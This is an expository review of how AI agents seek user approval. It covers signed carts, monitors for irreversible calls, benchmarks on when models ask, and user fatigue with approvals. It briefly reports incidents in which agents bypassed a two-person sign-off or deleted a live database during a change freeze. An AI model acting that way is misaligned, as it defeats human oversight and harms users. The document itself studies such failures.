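Existing approval systems differ in what the user signs. *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026) describes AP2, Google's payment protocol for agents, in which the user signs the contents of a shopping cart after seeing them on a trusted display. The paper contrasts AP2 with the common method of having the user confirm an action on a second device. That method produces a bearer token instead of a signature over the action's details, and the system requesting approval supplies those details.

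A user who sees exactly what they are approving can still approve the wrong thing. If a forged email raises the school's fee to $180, SUDP will accurately display a payment of $180, and the user has to notice that the amount is wrong. Approval also gives no protection if the agent can bypass it. *When AI Agents Act on Our Behalf* (Wang, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) describes a 2025 incident in which Amazon's Kiro agent inherited an engineer's access rights, bypassed the rule that two people must sign off on changes, and took a cloud service in mainland China offline for about 13 hours.

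### When one approval can cover several calls

Booking a weekend away might take ten calls, but the user makes only one or two decisions. Zhou and Zhang propose that a new call shouldn't need a new approval if it stays within a decision the user has already made. The user might approve a particular train and hotel for Saturday, for up to $190 in total. The assistant could then reserve, pay and download the tickets without asking again. It would have to ask before booking a different hotel if that one were full, or before spending more than $190.

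In SUDP, the user can sign a list of operations together after seeing the whole list. An operation can also specify how many times the custodian may run it before it expires. The limit is one for a payment, but low-risk actions that the assistant repeats often, such as reading the inbox, can be unlimited. A standing permission like this spares the user many questions, but the user no longer checks each use. Signing a list doesn't ensure that every operation on it will succeed, so the user could still end up with a train ticket but no hotel.

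### How a monitor could know that an action is irreversible

To apply the fifth policy, the monitor has to decide which calls to hold, and a tool's name often isn't enough. Pochampally (2026), in *DelegationBench*, gives the example of a user who asks an assistant to clean up generated files in the downloads folder. Moving a thumbnail to the bin is reversible for 30 days, but deleting it permanently is not. Both actions can use the same tool with a different value for one argument:

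```
remove_file(path="Downloads/preview.png", mode="trash")
remove_file(path="Downloads/preview.png", mode="permanent")
```

Yan's method of sorting tools by their descriptions doesn't look at the arguments of individual calls, so it would treat these two alike. Other actions depend on facts outside the call:

| Action | What determines whether it can be undone |
|---|---|
| Delete a photograph permanently | whether another copy exists |
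| Buy a train ticket | the refund conditions of that fare |
| Submit a hotel booking | whether the hotel accepts cancellations, and until when |
| Email the school | nothing, because the school can't be made to forget it |

Someone therefore has to record, for each tool and service, which effects are reversible and for how long. Zhou and Zhang note that only some services can cancel a submitted request, and that a refund may make up for a purchase but can't reverse a disclosure. If the record is incomplete, the monitor has to treat unknown actions as irreversible and ask the user more questions.

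The user or the harness can also make more actions reversible. The assistant could use the bin instead of permanent deletion, choose refundable fares, and wait ten minutes before sending mail. Wang and colleagues analysed 695 documented incidents and found that what people can stop or undo depends on how an agent is set up as well as on its model. In one incident, Replit's coding agent deleted a company's live database during a freeze on changes, and the founder learned of it only afterwards.

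### Do models ask at the right times?

If the monitor doesn't force a question, the model decides whether to ask. In AuthorizationBench, agents that consulted the user overstepped less often. DelegationBench tests when models choose to ask, using 156 short scenarios, each with an instruction, some context and a proposed action. The model can act, ask for permission, ask for a missing fact or refuse. The benchmark includes 48 pairs of scenarios designed to differ in one feature: whether the user requested the action, how much is at stake, whether the action can be undone, or whether other people will see the result.

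Three computer science students labelled the scenarios, and Pochampally compared their majority verdicts with the choices of ten models. The models acted in 20% to 59% of the cases where the students would have held back, and held back in 19% to 29% of the cases where the students would have acted. Making an action irreversible reduced how often models acted by 17 to 63 percentage points, depending on the model.

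These figures came from showing models an action and asking for a verdict. In a second test, models had to carry out 48 of the tasks themselves with simulated tools, and every model asked less often. Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite asked for permission in 47.5% of its verdicts but ended only 4.2% of the tasks with a question. The cause is unclear because the two tests differed in several ways. For instance, the second didn't mention permission or show the model a proposed action.

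Some questions were also hard to answer with a simple approval. When a task ended with a question, Pochampally replied "Yes, go ahead with that action." The model then called the tool in 97.5% of cases where it had asked a plain question about permission, 75% where the question mixed permission with a request for information, and 33% where the question concerned timing. A request that names one operation and needs only a yes or no avoids this problem.

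When given written rules, three of the models chose correctly between acting and asking at least 97% of the time. So users will probably get better results if they specify exactly when the assistant should ask than if they leave it to the model's judgment. But the test cases were short and artificial, and a monitor can enforce such a rule even when the model fails to apply it.

The benchmark is a rough guide to what users want, because the students often disagreed with one another and more than half of the pairs about stakes and reversibility also changed something else. The models were stricter than the students about actions that nobody had requested. In 8 of the 12 such cases, most of the students would have let the assistant go ahead.

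### What users complain about

*Babysitting AI Agents* (Mittal, Neville and colleagues, 2026) looked for both kinds of mistake in 163,487 Reddit posts from January 2025 to June 2026. Using a language model, the researchers found 6,623 descriptions of agents handling a task in a way the user hadn't expected. Of these, 4.2% were about agents that took consequential actions without asking, and 1.2% were about agents that asked needlessly. The largest category, at 15.4%, was agents that kept running without making progress. A harness can limit this by ending a task after a fixed number of refusals.

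The 4.2% is a share of complaints, so it doesn't measure how often agents fail to ask during tasks. The figures also don't show that asking too little is more than three times as common as asking too much, because people choose what to post and are probably more likely to report a deleted folder than an unnecessary question. Most of the posts also came from communities focused on coding or on running models at home.

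Mittal and colleagues surveyed 73 frequent users of agents to test how well such reports reflect experience. Each read scenarios for five of the study's 23 types of failure and said whether the same thing had happened to them. Types that were common on Reddit were no more likely than others to be common among these users. Unprompted recall was just as poor a guide to experience. Of the 16 people asked about excessive flattery, 13 had experienced it, but nobody in the study had mentioned it when asked to recall a failure.

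The survey also suggests why needless questions and actions taken without permission might produce different numbers of complaints. Participants rated needless questions 1.9 out of 5 for severity, among the lowest scores. They considered acting without permission more serious but harder to notice, and people can't complain about an action they never discover. The Reddit posts show that both problems occur and what they look like, but not how often they occur.

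### Do people check what they approve?

An approval protects users only if they consider the request. In Yan's experiment with a simulated assistant, seven of the 18 actions went beyond the task. One group of 34 participants had to approve or deny every action. They approved 40% of the unrequested actions, although the screen described each one in plain language.

In this group, 88% allowed the assistant to call the airport to confirm a flight, 35% allowed it to delete an old timesheet permanently, and 21% allowed it to announce publicly that the user was travelling. This variation suggests that people were paying some attention. They spent about eight seconds on each request.

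Yan measured what people approved but didn't measure whether they read the requests. Some approvals may have been deliberate, since a traveller might well welcome a call to the airport. The experiment was also short and had no real stakes, so it can't show how carefully busy people would read their 500th request after 499 harmless ones.

### The case for fewer requests and the case for more

The main argument for asking less often is that people get used to saying yes. Wang and colleagues cite earlier research in which people assigned to check an automated system came to accept its recommendations without real scrutiny. The same research found that the better a system performs, the less prepared people are to take over when it fails. Practitioners in *Let the Agent Do It?* based how closely they watched an agent on time and fatigue as well as risk. Constant questions also defeat the purpose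 of an assistant. One user in Mittal and colleagues' collection complained that supervising an agent took several times longer than doing the work.

The argument for asking more often is that some mistakes are permanent and only the user can recognise them. *Janus* (Brigham, Bagdasarian and colleagues, 2026) describes an email from someone who wants the details of a family reunion. The assistant may have no way to find out whether the sender is a relative. Answering an unnecessary question takes the user a few seconds, but the assistant can't take the details back once it has sent them to a stranger.

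Both arguments fit into one inequality. A question is worth asking if:

```
p × d × L  >  c
```

Here p is the chance that the user wouldn't want the action, d is the chance that the user notices this when asked, L is the harm if the action goes ahead, and c is the cost of the interruption. If one payment in 100 is wrong, each wrong payment would cost the user $200, and the user catches 60% of them when asked, then asking saves an average of $1.20 per payment. That may justify an eight-second interruption. For archiving a newsletter, L is close to zero, so asking isn't worthwhile.

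The two sides disagree mainly about d. If d stays the same however often the assistant asks, a few needless questions do little harm. But if each needless question makes the user less attentive, later questions protect the user less, including those about irreversible actions. Better rules can reduce the number of questions without removing the important ones. In Progent's AgentDojo tests, for example, only 6% of policy updates needed approval.

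### Janus: comparing ways to involve the user

Janus is a system for testing different answers to this problem. It checks a call against the user's lasting rules, and if they don't allow it, passes the call to a permission assistant that can consult the user. One design turns a single decision by the user into a broader rule, so that similar calls don't lead to more questions. However, that rule may be too broad. For example, the user may agree to send the reunion details to a cousin, but not to anyone who claims to be family.

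Brigham and colleagues compared six permission assistants in three scenarios. Input from the user could greatly improve privacy and security, and help from a model could make deciding easier. No design was best in every situation, and the researchers concluded that designers have to account for users getting tired of answering.

Three kinds of simulated user gave the answers in these tests. Comparing them can show what happens to a design if people become careless in a particular way, but not how soon real people become careless or whether a model's advice would make them more or less attentive.

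### Rules about consequences

Yan tested another approach with 35 participants, who each set four standing rules in advance. Each rule concerned a consequence, such as spending money, so it could cover many tools, and users didn't need to understand the tools' names. Yan compared this design with one in which the user approved every action and one in which a model allowed some actions and referred the rest to the user.

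| Design | Requests per person | Unrequested actions blocked | Total time deciding |
|---|---|---|---|
| Approve every action | 18.0 | 59.6% | 142 seconds |
| A model decides when to ask | 10.0 | 53.9% | 120 seconds |
| The user's own four rules | 10.9 | 39.6% | 129 seconds |

The rules reduced the number of requests but blocked the fewest unrequested actions, though the difference in blocking between the rules and the model's choices was not statistically significant after correction for multiple comparisons. The rules didn't reliably save time compared with approving everything, because participants first had to set them. They might save time over a longer period, since people set them only once.

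The protection was weak mostly because participants approved unrequested actions when asked. Of the 148 unrequested actions that went ahead under the rules, participants had approved 133, and "allow" rules had let through the other 15. Participants with rules approved 67% of the unrequested actions they were asked about, compared with 40% in the group that was asked about every action.

Part of this gap could arise because people who chose "never" no longer saw the requests they would have refused. But that can't explain all of it, because more unrequested actions also went ahead overall. Setting rules may have made participants feel they had already dealt with the risk. The experiment can't confirm this, and Yan recruited some of this group's participants separately after the initial random assignment.

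"Never" rules, by contrast, blocked all 31 of the unrequested actions they covered without asking the user. Participants chose them for only 16 of their 140 rules, most often for private information. When users would refuse a type of action every time, prohibiting it protects them better than asking each time, and leaves them fewer requests to review. Prohibitions don't help with spending or sending mail, which an assistant often has to do. Participants in all three groups reported a strong sense of control, including those whose rules had let most of the unrequested actions through.
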